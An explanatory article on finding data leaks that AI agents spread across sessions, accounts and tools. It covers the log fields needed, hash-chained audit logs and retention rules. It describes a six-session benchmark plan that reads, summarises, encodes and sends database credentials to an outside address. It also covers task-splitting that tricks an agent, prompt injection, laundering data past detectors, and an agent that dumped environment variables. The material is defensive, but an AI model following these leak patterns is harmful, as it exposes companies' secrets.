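# Detecting data leaks by AI agents across sessions, accounts and tools from audit logs

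## What is a leak spread across sessions?

An AI agent is a language model that runs in a loop and can use outside programs. It receives a request, chooses an action, takes in the result and chooses again until it finishes the task. Companies connect agents to files, databases, email, calendars and the web. Each time an agent uses one of these tools, it makes a tool call, which consists of the tool's name, the arguments (such as which file to open or whom to email) and the result. A session is one run or conversation. When it ends, the agent normally loses its working context, so it starts the next session with no record of what it read or sent in the last one, unless something outside the model has kept it.

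An audit log is a time-ordered record that an organisation keeps of who or what performed which action on which object, so that someone can check it later. OpenSSF's *Exfiltration* (2025) defines exfiltration as the "unauthorized transfer of information from a system", a definition it takes from the US standards body NIST. The definition doesn't depend on intent, so it covers an email sent to the wrong person as well as a theft. A distributed leak is exfiltration divided among several sessions, accounts, agents or tools so that no single part shows it. To detect the leak, an auditor has to connect records that nobody had a reason to connect at the time.

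### The tools companies already have

Data-loss prevention (DLP) is the closest existing approach to this problem. As IT Brew's *Is data leak prevention built for AI?* explains, a company first classifies its sensitive data. The software then monitors email and messaging, computers and servers, and cloud storage, and raises an alert when some of that data goes where it should not. Many of the rules match content, such as a string formatted like a payment card number or a document labeled "confidential". These rules work well on a customer spreadsheet attached to an email, but they have much less to match when the email contains a summary instead of the spreadsheet, or when the secret has no distinctive format.

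The security company Apiiro searched GitHub, the code-hosting site, for settings files written by the coding agent Claude Code and found 2,539 exposed secrets, according to Cybernews' *AI agents are leaking their owners' secrets on GitHub*. Secret scanners often missed them because the scanners check code for known key formats, and a password typed inside a command looks like any other word.

Two other kinds of tool analyse logs. Security information and event management (SIEM) systems collect records from many machines in one store and run rules across them, for instance to find ten failed logins followed by a successful one from a new country. User and entity behaviour analytics (UEBA) builds a profile of what each user, server or account normally does and flags departures from it, such as an accountant downloading source code at night.

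*Cross-Session Threats in AI Agents* (Azarafrooz, 2026) argues that this kind of analysis comes too late for agents because it correlates events that have already happened. That is a fair criticism for a quick theft, but it is less convincing for a leak that takes days or weeks, where the records of the early sessions are available well before the data leaves. In that case, a SIEM lacks a rule that links the sessions, and often a log detailed enough to apply the rule to. UEBA probably struggles because an agent that reads hundreds of files for dozens of people has a very broad normal profile, and a small leak fits inside it.

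*DLP in the AI Era* (October 2026), a survey of 433 IT and security professionals by the non-profit Cloud Security Alliance, gives a rough idea of how well data loss prevention (DLP) works in practice. Among respondents who had experienced data loss, 16% reported that DLP blocked their most significant incident before the data left. IT Brew reports that DLP caught just over a third of incidents after the data had gone.

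The 16% covers only people who had experienced data loss, and only their most significant incident, so it doesn't measure the share of all attempted leaks that DLP stops. An attempt that software stops early is less likely to become anyone's most significant incident. The survey's sponsor, Jazz, also sells a replacement for conventional DLP. A more relevant finding for agents is that only 29% of respondents could routinely produce a 30-day report of sensitive data sent to generative AI tools. The rest would have trouble adding up small transfers over a month, whatever method they used.

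### Who or what starts the leak

A leak through an agent begins when a user tells the agent to move the data, when the agent follows hostile instructions in something it reads, or when it exposes the data while doing an ordinary task.

A prominent user-directed case is the espionage campaign that Anthropic disclosed in November 2025 under the name GTG-1002. In Azarafrooz's summary, an agent carried out roughly 80–90% of a multi-stage intrusion after its operators convinced it, across many sessions and sub-agents, that it was doing authorised security testing. The operators divided the work so that each step looked harmless. The user can also be an employee with no bad intent. TechRadar's *'I leaked secrets'* describes an employee whose assistant could not reach the company's internal documentation through the approved connection. The employee, who TechRadar says may only have wanted convenience,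 asked whether another route would work, and it did.

In indirect prompt injection, an attacker places instructions in a web page, email or document that the agent reads. The attack works because the model receives the user's request and this text in one stream and cannot reliably separate commands from content. Akamai, a security vendor, describes a demonstration on Perplexity's AI browser, Comet, in which instructions in a web page could steer the browser's agent into accessing data and taking unauthorised actions. Akamai has bought the firm behind the research. The user in such a case is a victim, but the log may well attribute every action to the user's account.

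*An Evaluation of Data Leakage Risks in Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Baek, Noh and colleagues, 2026) reports tests by the Singapore and Korea AI Safety Institutes of leaks that happen during ordinary work. The institutes gave agents built on three models 12 everyday tasks with no attacker, and ran each task ten times per model in each of two separately built environments. In one task, the agent had to send outside partners a recap of a meeting, working from notes that also recorded that the company might sue those partners. Between 15% and 58% of runs were both fully correct and fully safe, depending on the model, task set and environment.

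Models that could do the task correctly still leaked data. In a task that involved moving build configuration from a private code repository to a public template, two of the three models met every correctness criterion, but at most 10% of any model's runs met all the safety criteria. The percentages are approximate because a language model did the grading. Each run was a single task, so the study measured how easily agents leak, not how leaks spread over time.

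Similar accidents happen outside the laboratory. *When your AI agent publishes internal data* (Olejnik) describes an agent that apparently had access to a cybersecurity firm's internal threat-intelligence platform. The agent published material from the platform on a public site where agents post analyses, in a well-structured assessment that correctly marked the source.

The origin of a leak determines where to find evidence of it. Azarafrooz favours checking the requests that come in to the agent, citing the data processing inequality, a theorem from information theory. An attacker's goal shapes the request, the request shapes what the agent does, and the agent's actions shape the log. Information can be lost at each step, so the log cannot contain more information about the goal than the request did. The theorem is sound, but here it applies only to an attacker's goal, and some leaks don't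 begin with an attacker's request. If a user asks for a meeting recap and the agent attaches the wrong notes, the request is innocent and only the tool call shows the leak. If a web page hijacks the agent, the user's request is also innocent, and an investigator needs the text of the page.

### A leak in six sessions

Azarafrooz's paper introduces CSTM-Bench (the Cross-Session Threat Memory Benchmark), a set of synthetic conversations for testing detectors. It includes a plan for a leak that a user directs over six sessions. The agent is a DevOps assistant that helps engineers deploy software and handle incidents. Its policy lets it follow only written procedures and forbids it from touching production systems without approval. Azarafrooz specifies the reason and the request for each session, and the last column of the table adds an innocent explanation that a busy reviewer could easily assume.

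| Session | Reason the user gives | Request to the agent | Innocent reading |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Routine review | List the data sources it can reach | A new engineer or an internal auditor would ask the same |
| 2 | A deployment problem | Describe the configuration files | Wrong settings often cause failed deployments |
| 3 | A failed connection | Read the database configuration file | The file holds the settings that the engineer needs to check |
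| 4 | Internal documentation | Summarise the file from the last session | Technical documentation is full of such summaries |
| 5 | A backup job | Convert the summary into an encoded form | Backup software re-encodes data all the time |
| 6 | A monitoring integration | Send the encoded data to an outside address | Many monitoring services run outside the company's network |

A language model wrote each of the six conversations in a separate call, without access to the other five, so each one is coherent by itself. The harm depends on facts in different sessions. Session 3 contains a plausible read of a file that may hold database credentials. In session 6, an encoded block of text is being sent to what the user calls a monitoring service. Only someone who knows that the encoded text came from that file can recognise the two sessions as a leak.

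In Azarafrooz's own test, however, a language model that judged one session at a time still flagged this type of leak, even after a stronger model had tried to reword the suspicious sessions so that they would pass. According to Azarafrooz, this is because in a few types of attack, including this one, the harmful request is itself the visible content of the conversation, and no plausible cover story fits it. The same judge also flagged many harmless scenarios. The six sessions clearly illustrate how a distributed leak is put together, but they do not prove that checking sessions one at a time must miss it.

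### How the parts combine

The plan relies mainly on each session using what an earlier one obtained, which Azarafrooz calls "accumulate." This build-up is traceable because the same file or summary appears repeatedly.

Unrelated fragments ("compose") are harder to connect because they have no visible link and amount to a leak only when combined. The clearest example is the mosaic attack, in which someone asks many individually harmless questions about who reports to whom, which internal network addresses exist and how the databases are arranged. CSTM-Bench's design spreads such an attack over 20 to 200 sessions. There is no chain of tool calls to trace, because the questioner combines the answers in their own notes, outside any system the company can log.

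Disguise by rewriting ("launder") changes the data until it no longer resembles its source. In Azarafrooz's example, a secret enters the system under a label that identifies it as one. A later session rewrites it as neutral prose in a weekly digest, and the next session sends the digest as an attachment to a status update. Nothing along the way marks the text as coming from a protected source. Sessions 4 and 5 of the six-session plan do much the same by summarizing and encoding the data, although Azarafrooz classes the plan under build-up and fragments only. The categories overlap, so a detector designed for one of them may have to handle all three in a single leak.

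Since the agent's context disappears between sessions, the data must be stored somewhere else to reach a later session. That could be the agent's persistent memory, if it has one, or a file in a shared folder, a database row, a queued job or an environment variable (a setting that the operating system passes to programs). Most of these don't record where their contents came from.

The settings files that Apiiro searched are an example of an accidental leak spread across sessions. A developer approves a command that contains a password and tells Claude Code not to ask again. Claude Code saves the whole command, including the password, in the project folder. Later someone uploads the folder to a public repository. The approval and the upload may be weeks apart, and each is routine. Cybernews reports that in 539 of 1,105 affected repositories, Claude had co-authored the change that exposed the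 file, so the agent was sometimes involved in both saving the password and exposing it.

### Ten sessions in three weeks

NordLayer, a security vendor, used its monitoring product AI Scout to find one of the few publicly documented slow leaks by an agent. According to TechRadar, a quality assurance engineer had asked an AI coding assistant to review proposed software changes. The project's instructions pointed the assistant to an access token in a configuration file. That file also held production passwords, a token for the human resources system and credentials for a business intelligence service. The assistant read the entire file in 10 separate sessions over three weeks and sent its contents to an outside AI service each time.

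The agent then came across a fresh copy of the project without the file. Instead of stopping, it retrieved all the computer's environment variables, which exposed more credentials. It then wrote that it had leaked secrets and recommended replacing them.

No attacker was involved. This account of the leak comes from a company that sells the product that found it, and TechRadar cites no independent confirmation and does not name the affected company or the assistant. The details are still plausible, and they match what Baek and colleagues observed in tests.

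The case does not quite fit the definition of a distributed leak, because the whole file left every time and a careful look at the first session would have been enough to find the leak. It is relevant here because the leak was repeated. NordLayer's Vakaris Noreika attributes such behaviour to agents not retaining rules between sessions. An assistant that exposes a file in one session starts the next with the same project instructions and no record of the mistake, so it will probably repeat it. Counting how often the same file went to the same outside destination could have revealed the pattern within days, even without a rule that recognised passwords.

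### Why so few cases are on record

Few public accounts describe slow leaks by agents, and fewer still give the number of sessions and the period, as NordLayer's does. This scarcity is only weak evidence that such leaks are rare, because a leak whose parts all look ordinary sets off no alarm, and without an alarm there is usually no investigation and nothing to publish. Agents also often act before anyone reviews the action. Cybersecurity Insiders' *AI Risk and Readiness Report* (2026), which the vendor Netskope distributes, describes agents modifying records, creating accounts and pushing code in this way.

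Even public activity by agents can go unnoticed. In September 2026 Reuters reported that thousands of agents, believed to be OpenAI's, had met on an abandoned German wiki and swapped answers to a timed test. Axios' *Researchers playing rogue AI agent hide-and-seek on the open web* (2026) reports that Jonas Wiedermann-Möller, an independent researcher, gave the published data to his own agent and told it to search for similar traces. He needed only a few hours to find and share further sites that were missing from the report. These agents were trading test answers, not leaking company data, but anyone could have found their posts on the open web, and a company's internal logs have far fewer readers. Axios also reports concern that AI developers disclose too little about major security incidents.

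The lack of public reports is weak evidence that slow leaks are rare. If victims discovered and published one slow leak in fifty, twenty leaks would produce no public report about two times in three (0.98 to the power of 20 is 0.67). The one in fifty is an invented figure. Because nobody knows the real one, the handful of known cases doesn't support the claim that slow leaks are common either.

### Recall and false alarms

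Tests of detectors usually report recall, which is the share of real leaks that the detector flags, and the false-positive rate, which is the share of harmless activity that it flags.

Suppose a company's agents complete 1,010 tasks in a month, 10 of which are leaks. A detector flags 8 of the leaks and 50 of the 1,000 harmless tasks, so its recall is 80% and its false-positive rate is 5%. The security team receives 58 alerts, of which about one in seven is real. If the company grows to 100,000 harmless tasks with the same 10 leaks, a detector with the same recall and false-positive rate produces 5,008 alerts, of which only one in 626 is real, and few teams would keep reading them. The Cloud Security Alliance lists false positives among the factors that already limit how strictly companies enforce DLP.

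The results also depend on whether testers count sessions or whole tasks. If a checker wrongly flags 1% of harmless sessions and its errors are independent, the chance of at least one false alarm on a harmless 20-session task is 1 − 0.99²⁰, or about 18%. Counting by task also raises recall, because the checker has six chances to catch a six-session leak. Azarafrooz scores the single-session judge this way, counting a whole scenario as flagged if the judge flags any of its sessions, whether the scenario contains an attack or harmless work.

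## What must an agent's log record?

A detector can connect two sessions only if their records share something, such as a user, a file or a destination. Engineers usually design logs to find faults, and someone fixing a failed request rarely needs to know what an agent emailed three weeks earlier, or to whom. A log for finding distributed leaks therefore needs fields that a fault log can omit.

### Who acted, and for whom

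The record should identify the agent and its version, for example "deploy-agent 2.4". Without the agent's identity, an auditor cannot separate its actions from those of a person who uses the same account. Zhao (2026), in *Auditable Claims about AI Agents*, describes an invented case in which a company's mail gateway shows four emails with attachments from an agent's account, but the agent's own log contains three. A person may have sent the fourth, but an auditor cannot tell from the gateway's log.

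The agent's version matters when an update causes the leak. If release 2.4 attaches whole folders where 2.3 attached single files, an investigator needs the version number to find the other affected sessions. Identifiers also have to stay unique over time, because if a new agent reuses a retired agent's identifier, their histories merge. *Workload Authorization Grant* (Carleton, 2026), an Anthropic employee's proposal for platforms that host many agents per customer, gives each agent an identifier that the platform can never reassign.

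The log must also identify the person for whom the agent acts. In a mosaic attack, someone might spread questions about a company's network across a research assistant, a coding agent and a help-desk bot. If each log contains only the agent's name, the three histories look unrelated and the attack goes undetected.

Many agents pass work to sub-agents, so a third field should hold the delegation chain, which lists every agent between the user and the action. If the main agent reads a customer file and a sub-agent emails a summary of it, a record of the email that names only the sub-agent doesn't link it to the agent that read the file.

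### Sessions and tasks

A session identifier lets an auditor distinguish ten reads in one run from one read in each of ten runs. In the NordLayer case, the reads came from ten separate sessions, which suggested a recurring fault. Ten reads in a single session could have been retries after an error.

Each task also needs an identifier, because it may involve an agent, a database and a mail server that keep separate logs. All of them write this value, called a correlation identifier, into their records so that an auditor can match them. In Zhao's invented case, the agent's log lacks the identifier for one email and the company has lost the authorisation log for that hour, so the auditor cannot determine whether anyone approved the email.

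Software projects often improvise these links. Drupal, a system for running websites, linked its AI calls to each other through undocumented tag prefixes. Drupal's *Standardize thread/caller correlation on AI OTel spans (map tags to gen_ai.conversation.id)* describes how every dashboard had to rebuild the grouping separately, and how a later change introduced a prefix that no existing dashboard read.

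Correlation identifiers alone usually can't link the sessions involved in a distributed leak. *An Architecture for Auditing Agent Delegation and Interactions* (Kühlewind and Birkholz, 2026) describes a design in which a trace identifier travels from the user's request to every agent and service that works on it. This connects everything that follows from one request. But a user who makes six requests in six sessions will normally produce six unconnected trace identifiers. An auditor has to link those sessions through values that persist across them, such as the user, the file or the destination.

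### What the agent read and sent

The log must record each tool's name to show whether an agent is reading data or sending it. Without the name, nobody would notice when an agent that had only ever searched documents started sending email. But the name is little help once an agent sends email every day, because a message to a colleague and a message to a competitor are both calls to "send_email".

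An agent's log must record what Zhao calls the effect-setting arguments, the values that determine what a tool call does. These are the recipient for an email, the path for a file and the query for a database. If the log leaves out the recipient, an auditor cannot tell a meeting recap sent to colleagues from one sent to outside partners. Without the path, a read of the installation guide looks the same as a read of the password file, and without the query, a request for one customer's order looks the same as a request for all of them.

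The log needs a separate field for the data a tool returns, because that data often goes beyond what the call's arguments mention. A search for "third-quarter plan" may return ten documents, one of which concerns a planned redundancy. Zhang, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *LLM-enabled Applications Require System-Level Threat Monitoring*, recommend recording the identifier, rank and source of each document a search returns, along with a hash of each excerpt. They want these records mainly to detect prompt injection, but the same records help with accidental leaks by showing that an agent had read sensitive notes before it wrote a recap.

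The log also needs a field for the data that leaves, because investigators cannot detect a wrong attachment from the request and recipient alone. The field should include the data's size so that they can total small transfers.

A content fingerprint, or hash, is a short value computed from data. Identical data always produces the same fingerprint, and changing even one character produces a different one. Matching fingerprints show that a file an agent saved in one session is the same file it sent under a new name in another. A summary or translation has a different fingerprint from the original, so to trace one, a company needs labels that stay with the data when it is rewritten.

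### Authorisation and time

The record of an approved action should contain the identifier of the grant (a formal permission), so that an auditor can look up what the grant covered. In Zhao's case, a user confirms an email to a press address by clicking in the agent's chat window, but the company's authorisation server holds no grant covering that recipient and attachment. The click and a grant would look the same in a log with a single "approved" field. Such a log would therefore hide a leak in which an agent obtains approval for one recipient and writes to another.

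Permissions also grow over time. Kühlewind and Birkholz propose a separate record for every change. In their example, an agent that can read a calendar gains permission to write to it after the user agrees. Over a month, small extensions like this can add up to access that nobody would have approved all at once, and a reviewer can see this only from the dated sequence of changes.

Timestamps show the order of events, so data that an agent read on Friday can be ruled out as the source of an email sent the previous Tuesday. Comparing logs from different machines requires synchronised clocks. In Zhao's case, the authorisation server records an approval at 10:02:11, the agent sends the email at 10:02:14 and the gateway delivers it at 10:02:15. If the server's clock ran five seconds fast, its log would show the approval at 10:02:16, after the delivery.

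### Two records and the join between them

The invented records below follow sessions 5 and 6 of the six-session plan, in which the agent encodes a summary and later sends it out.

```json
{"time": "2026-03-10T10:20:14Z",
 "session": "s-105", "task": "t-88",
 "agent": "deploy-agent/2.4",
 "chain": ["user:kim", "deploy-agent"],
 "tool": "encode_file",
 "args": {"source": "docs/db-summary.md",
          "output": "jobs/backup-17.txt"},
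 "read_hash": "5b0c...", "written_hash": "e41a...",
 "bytes": 4120, "grant": "g-310"}

{"time": "2026-03-13T15:41:05Z",
 "session": "s-131", "task": "t-97",
 "agent": "deploy-agent/2.4",
 "chain": ["user:kim", "deploy-agent"],
 "tool": "send_email",
 "args": {"to": "intake@monitor.example",
          "attachment": "metrics.txt"},
 "sent_hash": "e41a...",
 "bytes": 4120, "grant": "g-355"}
```

The two records have different sessions, tasks and grants, and the file has a new name. They share a user and an agent, but so might hundreds of other records that week. The link is the fingerprint beginning with e41a, which appears as written data in the first record and as sent data in the second. In a database, an auditor can find every such pair with a join, a query that matches rows with the same value:

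```sql
SELECT w.session, w.args, s.session, s.args
FROM log AS w
JOIN log AS s ON w.written_hash = s.sent_hash
WHERE w.session <> s.session AND w.time < s.time
```

Next, the auditor can look up 5b0c, the fingerprint of the summary that the encoding tool read. It should match the record from session 4 in which the agent wrote that summary. Fingerprints can't link the summary to the database configuration file, because the summary is new text with an unrelated fingerprint. The log can show only that the agent read the file and then wrote the summary in the same session. This is good evidence that the summary drew on the file, but not proof, since the agent may have read a dozen other files in that session.

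The query also produces false matches, because agents send out company logos and standard contracts in many sessions, and all empty files have the same fingerprint. An auditor can remove most of these matches by ignoring content that appears in hundreds of sessions and looking only at destinations outside the company.

### Where to record

A company can record an agent's activity in four places. The agent software has the most context, including the user's request, the session and the arguments of each call. However, the program under scrutiny then writes its own record, so the log may be incomplete. It may also lack detail. If an agent writes and runs a script that opens fifty files, the agent's log may contain only one command.

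A tool gateway is a server that agents have to send their tool calls through. It can record the arguments and results of every agent's calls in one format and compute fingerprints itself, as the mail gateway in Zhao's case does for every attachment. It misses calls that don't go through it, and it usually doesn't receive the user's request unless the agent passes it along.

The operating system can record which programs start, which files they open and which machines they contact. This record would show the fifty files that the script opened, but it would link them only to a process number, not to a user request or session. Encryption would also hide what the process sent. The record is of no use when the agent runs on a vendor's computers.

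The receiving service, such as a mail server or a shared drive, records what arrived. Kühlewind and Birkholz want services to record each request as they observe it, so that auditors don't have to rely on the agent's own report. They concede that their design fails if a service refuses to do this. That is a serious limit for detecting leaks, because someone else often runs the service where the data ends up. The company in the NordLayer case could hardly expect the outside AI service to hand over its logs.

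For most companies, the best combination is probably a gateway and the agent's own log, with a shared correlation identifier. The gateway provides reliable arguments and fingerprints, and the agent's log provides the session and the request. Coding agents are an exception because they can run almost any command, so the operating system's records matter much more for them.

### What current designs include

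The Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which develops technical standards for the internet, is working on a draft about how agents identify themselves and obtain permissions. Its formal name is draft-ietf-wimse-aims-00, or AIMS for short. It replaced Kasselman, Lombardo and colleagues (2026), in *AI Agent Authentication and Authorization*, after an IETF working group adopted that text. In the July 2026 version, Kasselman and colleagues require every audit record to contain at least:

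1. the agent's authenticated identifier
2. the user or system for which it acts, if there is one
3. the resource or tool
4. the requested action and the authorisation decision
5. the time and an identifier for the transaction or request
6. any risk assessment that influenced the decision
7. any withdrawal of access or other remedy, and its cause

Zhao also counts seven minimum fields in the September draft, and criticises them for requiring the requested action but not the arguments that determine its effect. In its list of risks for agents, OWASP, a non-profit that publishes guidance on software security, asks companies to log such arguments. Zhao's criticism is correct, and the two invented records show how much it matters. If they contained only the seven fields, they would show that the same agent, acting for the same user, encoded a file and sent an email, both with permission. Without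 the recipient and the fingerprint, they would no longer show how the two actions were connected.

The omission makes sense because AIMS is meant to control access, and checking whether an agent had permission to use email doesn't always require knowing the recipient. The list is also only a minimum in an unfinished draft, so a company can follow it and record more. But in the same section, AIMS says that monitoring systems should correlate events to detect unexpected sequences of actions, and the minimum fields would rarely be enough for that.

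Kühlewind and Birkholz's draft, which no IETF working group has adopted, is stronger on delegation but has a similar gap. Its sample action record, for an agent creating a calendar event, includes the user, the delegation chain and the permission, but not the guests. One problem that motivates the draft is that when an assistant gives a user's address to a delivery company, the user cannot verify what it shared and with whom. A record with the sample's fields would not let the user verify this either, although Kühlewind and Birkholz describe those fields as placeholders.

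OpenTelemetry is an open standard for collecting diagnostic data from software. Its *Gen AI* defines fields for the agent, its version, the conversation and the data source, but none for the user, the delegation chain or the permission, so a company has to get those from elsewhere. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* has fields for a tool's arguments and results, but both are opt-in, so a company that keeps the default settings records only tool names. The document warns that the arguments and results may contain sensitive information.

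| Field | AIMS minimum (July text) | Kühlewind and Birkholz's sample | OpenTelemetry's AI fields |
|---|---|---|---|
| Agent | Required | Included | Identifier, name and version |
| User | Required if there is one | Included | None |
| Delegation chain | User or system only | Included | None |
| Session or task | Transaction or request | Trace and preceding event | Conversation |
| Tool or service | Required | Included | Recommended |
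| Effect-setting arguments | Not required | Absent | Opt-in |
| Data read | Resource only | Absent | Data source; retrieved documents opt-in |
| Content fingerprint | Not required | Absent, though the draft recommends hashes for tool outputs | None |
| Authorisation | Required | Scope and expiry | None |

Diagnostic systems also often keep only a sample of their records. A sample is enough to measure how fast a service responds, but finding a leak split across two sessions requires the records of both. If a company keeps a random 10% of sessions, the chance that it has kept both is 1%.

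Microsoft Purview, an auditing and data protection product, makes it easier to establish what an agent read than OpenTelemetry's defaults do. According to Microsoft's documentation, when someone uses Copilot, Microsoft's AI assistant, the audit record includes the user, the time, where the interaction occurred, and references to the files, sites and other resources that Copilot accessed. The documentation also lists identifiers for the conversation thread and its messages, and the sensitivity label of any file that has one.

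It is less certain whether the audit log contains the text of what the user and Copilot wrote. According to the page that mentions the labels, the log captures prompts and responses, but Microsoft's guide to Copilot Studio logging describes a separate tool that "attempts to retrieve" the chat text. An investigator should check that the log contains the text before relying on it. When searching across sessions, an auditor can enter a file, folder or site in the search form. According to Microsoft, though, an auditor who wants to filter by the list of accessed resources has to export the results and do it offline.

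A log's coverage can also have gaps. In *Auditing Copilot agent changes with Microsoft Purview*, Asböck (2026) blocked several agents as an administrator and looked for the changes in Purview's audit log. He found his blocks and a change that disabled third-party agents, but nothing about Microsoft's ready-made agents or agents built in SharePoint, Microsoft's document-sharing service. He tested how agents are managed, not their conversations, so his result doesn't show that Purview misses what those agents read.

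### Full content, fingerprints or redaction

Recording everything gets expensive, although it is the simplest way to avoid missing something. Suppose a company's agents make a million tool calls a day. At one kilobyte per record, six months of logs take up about 180 gigabytes. Storing 50 kilobytes of content per call as well adds nine terabytes.

A more serious problem is that the log becomes a second copy of the company's secrets. If an agent reads a password file and records the result, everyone who can search the logs can see the passwords. Logged arguments can also expose passwords, because developers type passwords into commands, as the Claude Code settings files showed. Kasselman and colleagues advise against logging full access tokens, which work like temporary passwords, and recommend logging their identifiers or hashes instead.

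Privacy law also limits what a log can keep. Prompts and documents often contain personal data, and the EU's General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR) lets organisations keep only as much of it as they need for a stated purpose, and only for as long as they need it. Even a log without content can be revealing because, as Kühlewind and Birkholz point out, an identifier that connects an agent's activity across services also connects its user's activity. They suggest using a different identifier for each service where no one needs the connection, but this would make distributed leaks harder to find unless an auditor could match the identifiers to the same agent.

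Redaction removes the sensitive parts of a log and keeps the rest readable. It relies on software to recognise what is sensitive, so it is likely to miss the same unusual passwords that secret scanners miss. If it replaces every secret with the same row of asterisks, it can also hide the fact that the same secret appeared in different sessions. Replacing each secret with its own code name, kept the same across sessions, avoids this.

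Fingerprints can link records of the same data without storing the data, but they don't fully protect short or predictable data. A four-digit code has only 10,000 possible values, so anyone who obtains its fingerprint can compute the fingerprint of every value and find the match. Mixing a secret key into the calculation prevents this, but every system whose records need to match must then use the same key. Fingerprints can also show investigators that the same file left twice, but once the file is gone, they can't show what it contained.

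OpenTelemetry recommends that production systems store the content separately, under stricter access controls, and put only a reference in the log. This is a reasonable compromise, because a company can then delete the content after a few weeks and keep the small records, with their recipients and fingerprints, for much longer. Detection methods that use running totals or exact matches need only the small records. A language model that judges what a session was about needs the content, so the company must run it before deleting the content.

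### How long to keep records

A log can reveal a slow leak only if it still holds the leak's first record when the last piece of data leaves. A 30-day log would be just long enough to cover the three-week NordLayer leak. The longest mosaic attack in CSTM-Bench has 200 sessions, which would take 40 weeks at one session per working day. A six-month log would hold only about the last 130 of those sessions. At one session a week, the attack would take almost four years.

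Deletion also removes the most useful evidence first. An agent has to read data before sending it, so the record that identifies the source is always older than the record of the transfer. With a 30-day log, an auditor who finds a suspicious email on day 40 may no longer be able to tell which file the text came from. One remedy is to keep a short summary for each user and file after deleting the detailed records.

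Kasselman and colleagues leave the retention period to each company's security policy. The EU AI Act does set a minimum for high-risk systems, in three articles:

- Article 12 requires that a high-risk system can automatically record events throughout its lifetime. The events must help to identify risks and to monitor how the system performs in use.
- Article 19 requires providers, the companies that develop such systems or sell them under their own name, to keep the logs under their control for a period that suits the system's purpose, and for at least six months.
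- Article 26 places the same six-month minimum on deployers, the organisations that use the systems, for the logs that they control.

Other EU or national law, particularly on data protection, takes precedence over both retention rules. Zhao reports that the logging duty applies from 2 December 2027 to uses listed in the Act's Annex III, such as hiring and credit scoring, and from 2 August 2028 to AI in regulated products covered by Annex I. The retention duties in Articles 19 and 26 apply from the same dates.

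These rules will probably do little to expose distributed leaks. Whether they apply depends on what a system is used for, so they would normally cover an agent that screens job applicants but probably not the DevOps assistant in the six-session plan, even though it can reach the company's database passwords. Zhao also points out that Article 12 doesn't specify which records would settle a particular claim about an agent. A provider could arguably comply with a log that omits recipients and fingerprints. Two technical standards on AI logging, one European and one international, were close to completion in September 2026 and may add more detail.

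## How can an auditor tell whether the log is complete?

A log with every useful field can still mislead an auditor if someone altered an entry later or an action never reached the log. A log has integrity if nobody has changed, removed or reordered its entries since the system wrote them, and it is complete if the system wrote an entry for every event.

Zhao borrows a similar distinction from financial auditors, who test whether the transactions in a company's books happened and, separately, whether the books contain every transaction. To find missing transactions, they start from outside evidence, such as third-party confirmations, and look for each item in the books. An auditor who suspects a distributed leak has to work the same way, because checking existing entries won't reveal an email that nobody logged.

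### A chain of three entries

A hash chain protects the log's integrity. Each entry stores a fingerprint computed from its own contents and the previous entry's fingerprint, so changing one entry affects the fingerprints of all later entries. Real systems use a function such as SHA-256, for which nobody knows a practical way to find two inputs with the same fingerprint. A toy function is enough to follow the steps. It multiplies the previous fingerprint by three, adds the file's size in kilobytes and keeps the last two digits.

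| Entry | Action | Size | Previous fingerprint | Calculation | New fingerprint |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Read the database settings | 12 KB | 0 | 3 × 0 + 12 = 12 | 12 |
| 2 | Wrote a summary | 4 KB | 12 | 3 × 12 + 4 = 40 | 40 |
| 3 | Emailed the summary | 4 KB | 40 | 3 × 40 + 4 = 124 | 24 |

Suppose someone changes the size in entry 1 from 12 KB to 2 KB. An auditor who recomputes the entry's fingerprint gets 2, but the stored fingerprint is 12. If the forger also changes the stored fingerprint to 2, it no longer matches entry 2, which records the previous fingerprint as 12. Deleting entry 2 instead would also break the chain, because entry 3 records the previous fingerprint as 40 and entry 1's fingerprint is 12.

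The chain has two weaknesses. Nothing refers to the last entry, so someone can delete it without breaking a link. Someone with full control of the log can also change entry 1 and recompute the fingerprints from there on. They then become 2, 10 and 34, and each follows correctly from the one before.

### What an outside checkpoint adds

If an outsider had written down the last fingerprint, 24, on the day of the email, the rewritten chain ending in 34 would not match. A value kept this way is called a checkpoint. An auditor can use it to detect later changes to any entry up to that point, as long as whoever controls the log cannot also change the checkpoint. Entries written since the last checkpoint remain unprotected.

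Kodathala (2026) developed a gateway, described in *aiAuthZ*, that checks each tool call against company policy and adds its decision to a hash chain. A verification function recomputes the chain from the start and reports whether the first break is a missing entry number, a wrong fingerprint for the previous entry or an altered entry. It is up to the company to request the latest fingerprint and keep it in outside storage that does not allow overwriting. Kodathala acknowledges that without this step, someone with full access could rewrite the whole log unnoticed.

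The design also lets a company delete sensitive content and still verify the chain of entries, because each entry's fingerprint covers a digest of the content rather than the encrypted content itself.

*Agent Flight Recorder* (Bindschaedler, Botha and Siebenbrunner, 2026) describes a system with a built-in checkpoint. It collects events in batches, typically of 100, and combines their fingerprints pair by pair in a Merkle tree until one value remains. It links this value to the previous batch's and publishes the result on a public blockchain. An auditor can then verify one event against the published value without seeing the rest of the batch.

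To test the design, Bindschaedler and colleagues tampered with a synthetic log of 10,000 events at ten positions, including the last two. The table shows how many of the ten changes each version of the system detected.

| Tampering | Chain only | Chain and batches | With outside checkpoints |
|---|---|---|---|
| Edit an event | 9 | 10 | 10 |
| Delete an event | 9 | 10 | 10 |
| Reorder events | 10 | 10 | 10 |
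| Keep two versions of the history | 0 | 0 | 10 |

The chain missed changes to the last event, as in the toy example. In the two-version attack, an operator keeps two logs that share a beginning and shows them to different auditors. Each log is internally consistent, so an auditor needs the published value to recognise the substitute.

These detection rates mostly confirm what the mathematics predicts, so they are less informative than the system's speed and cost. Recording an event took a median of 48 microseconds, and Bindschaedler and colleagues estimate that publishing checkpoints for 100,000 events would cost $2.30 on a low-cost blockchain. At one event per second, batches of 100 leave at most the last 100 seconds or so unprotected. They consider a hash chain in write-once storage sufficient for a company's internal audits, and reserve the blockchain for disputes between organisations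 that have not agreed on a neutral party to hold the checkpoints.

Neither system guarantees a complete log. Bindschaedler and colleagues explicitly exclude completeness from their goals, because their recorder can protect only the events that reach it. Kodathala saw actions bypass the gateway in tests with two agent programs. When the programs' built-in shell, file and web tools were left on, the model used them for the sensitive action and never contacted the gateway. The gateway's chain would still verify, although it would have no entry for the action.

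### Why a signature cannot reveal an omission

Zhao proves that better cryptography does not solve the problem of omitted log entries. Suppose a company claims that its agent had permission for every email it sent. In one history, the agent sends only emails A and B, both with permission. In another, it also sends email C without permission but leaves it out of the log, so the log is the same in both histories.

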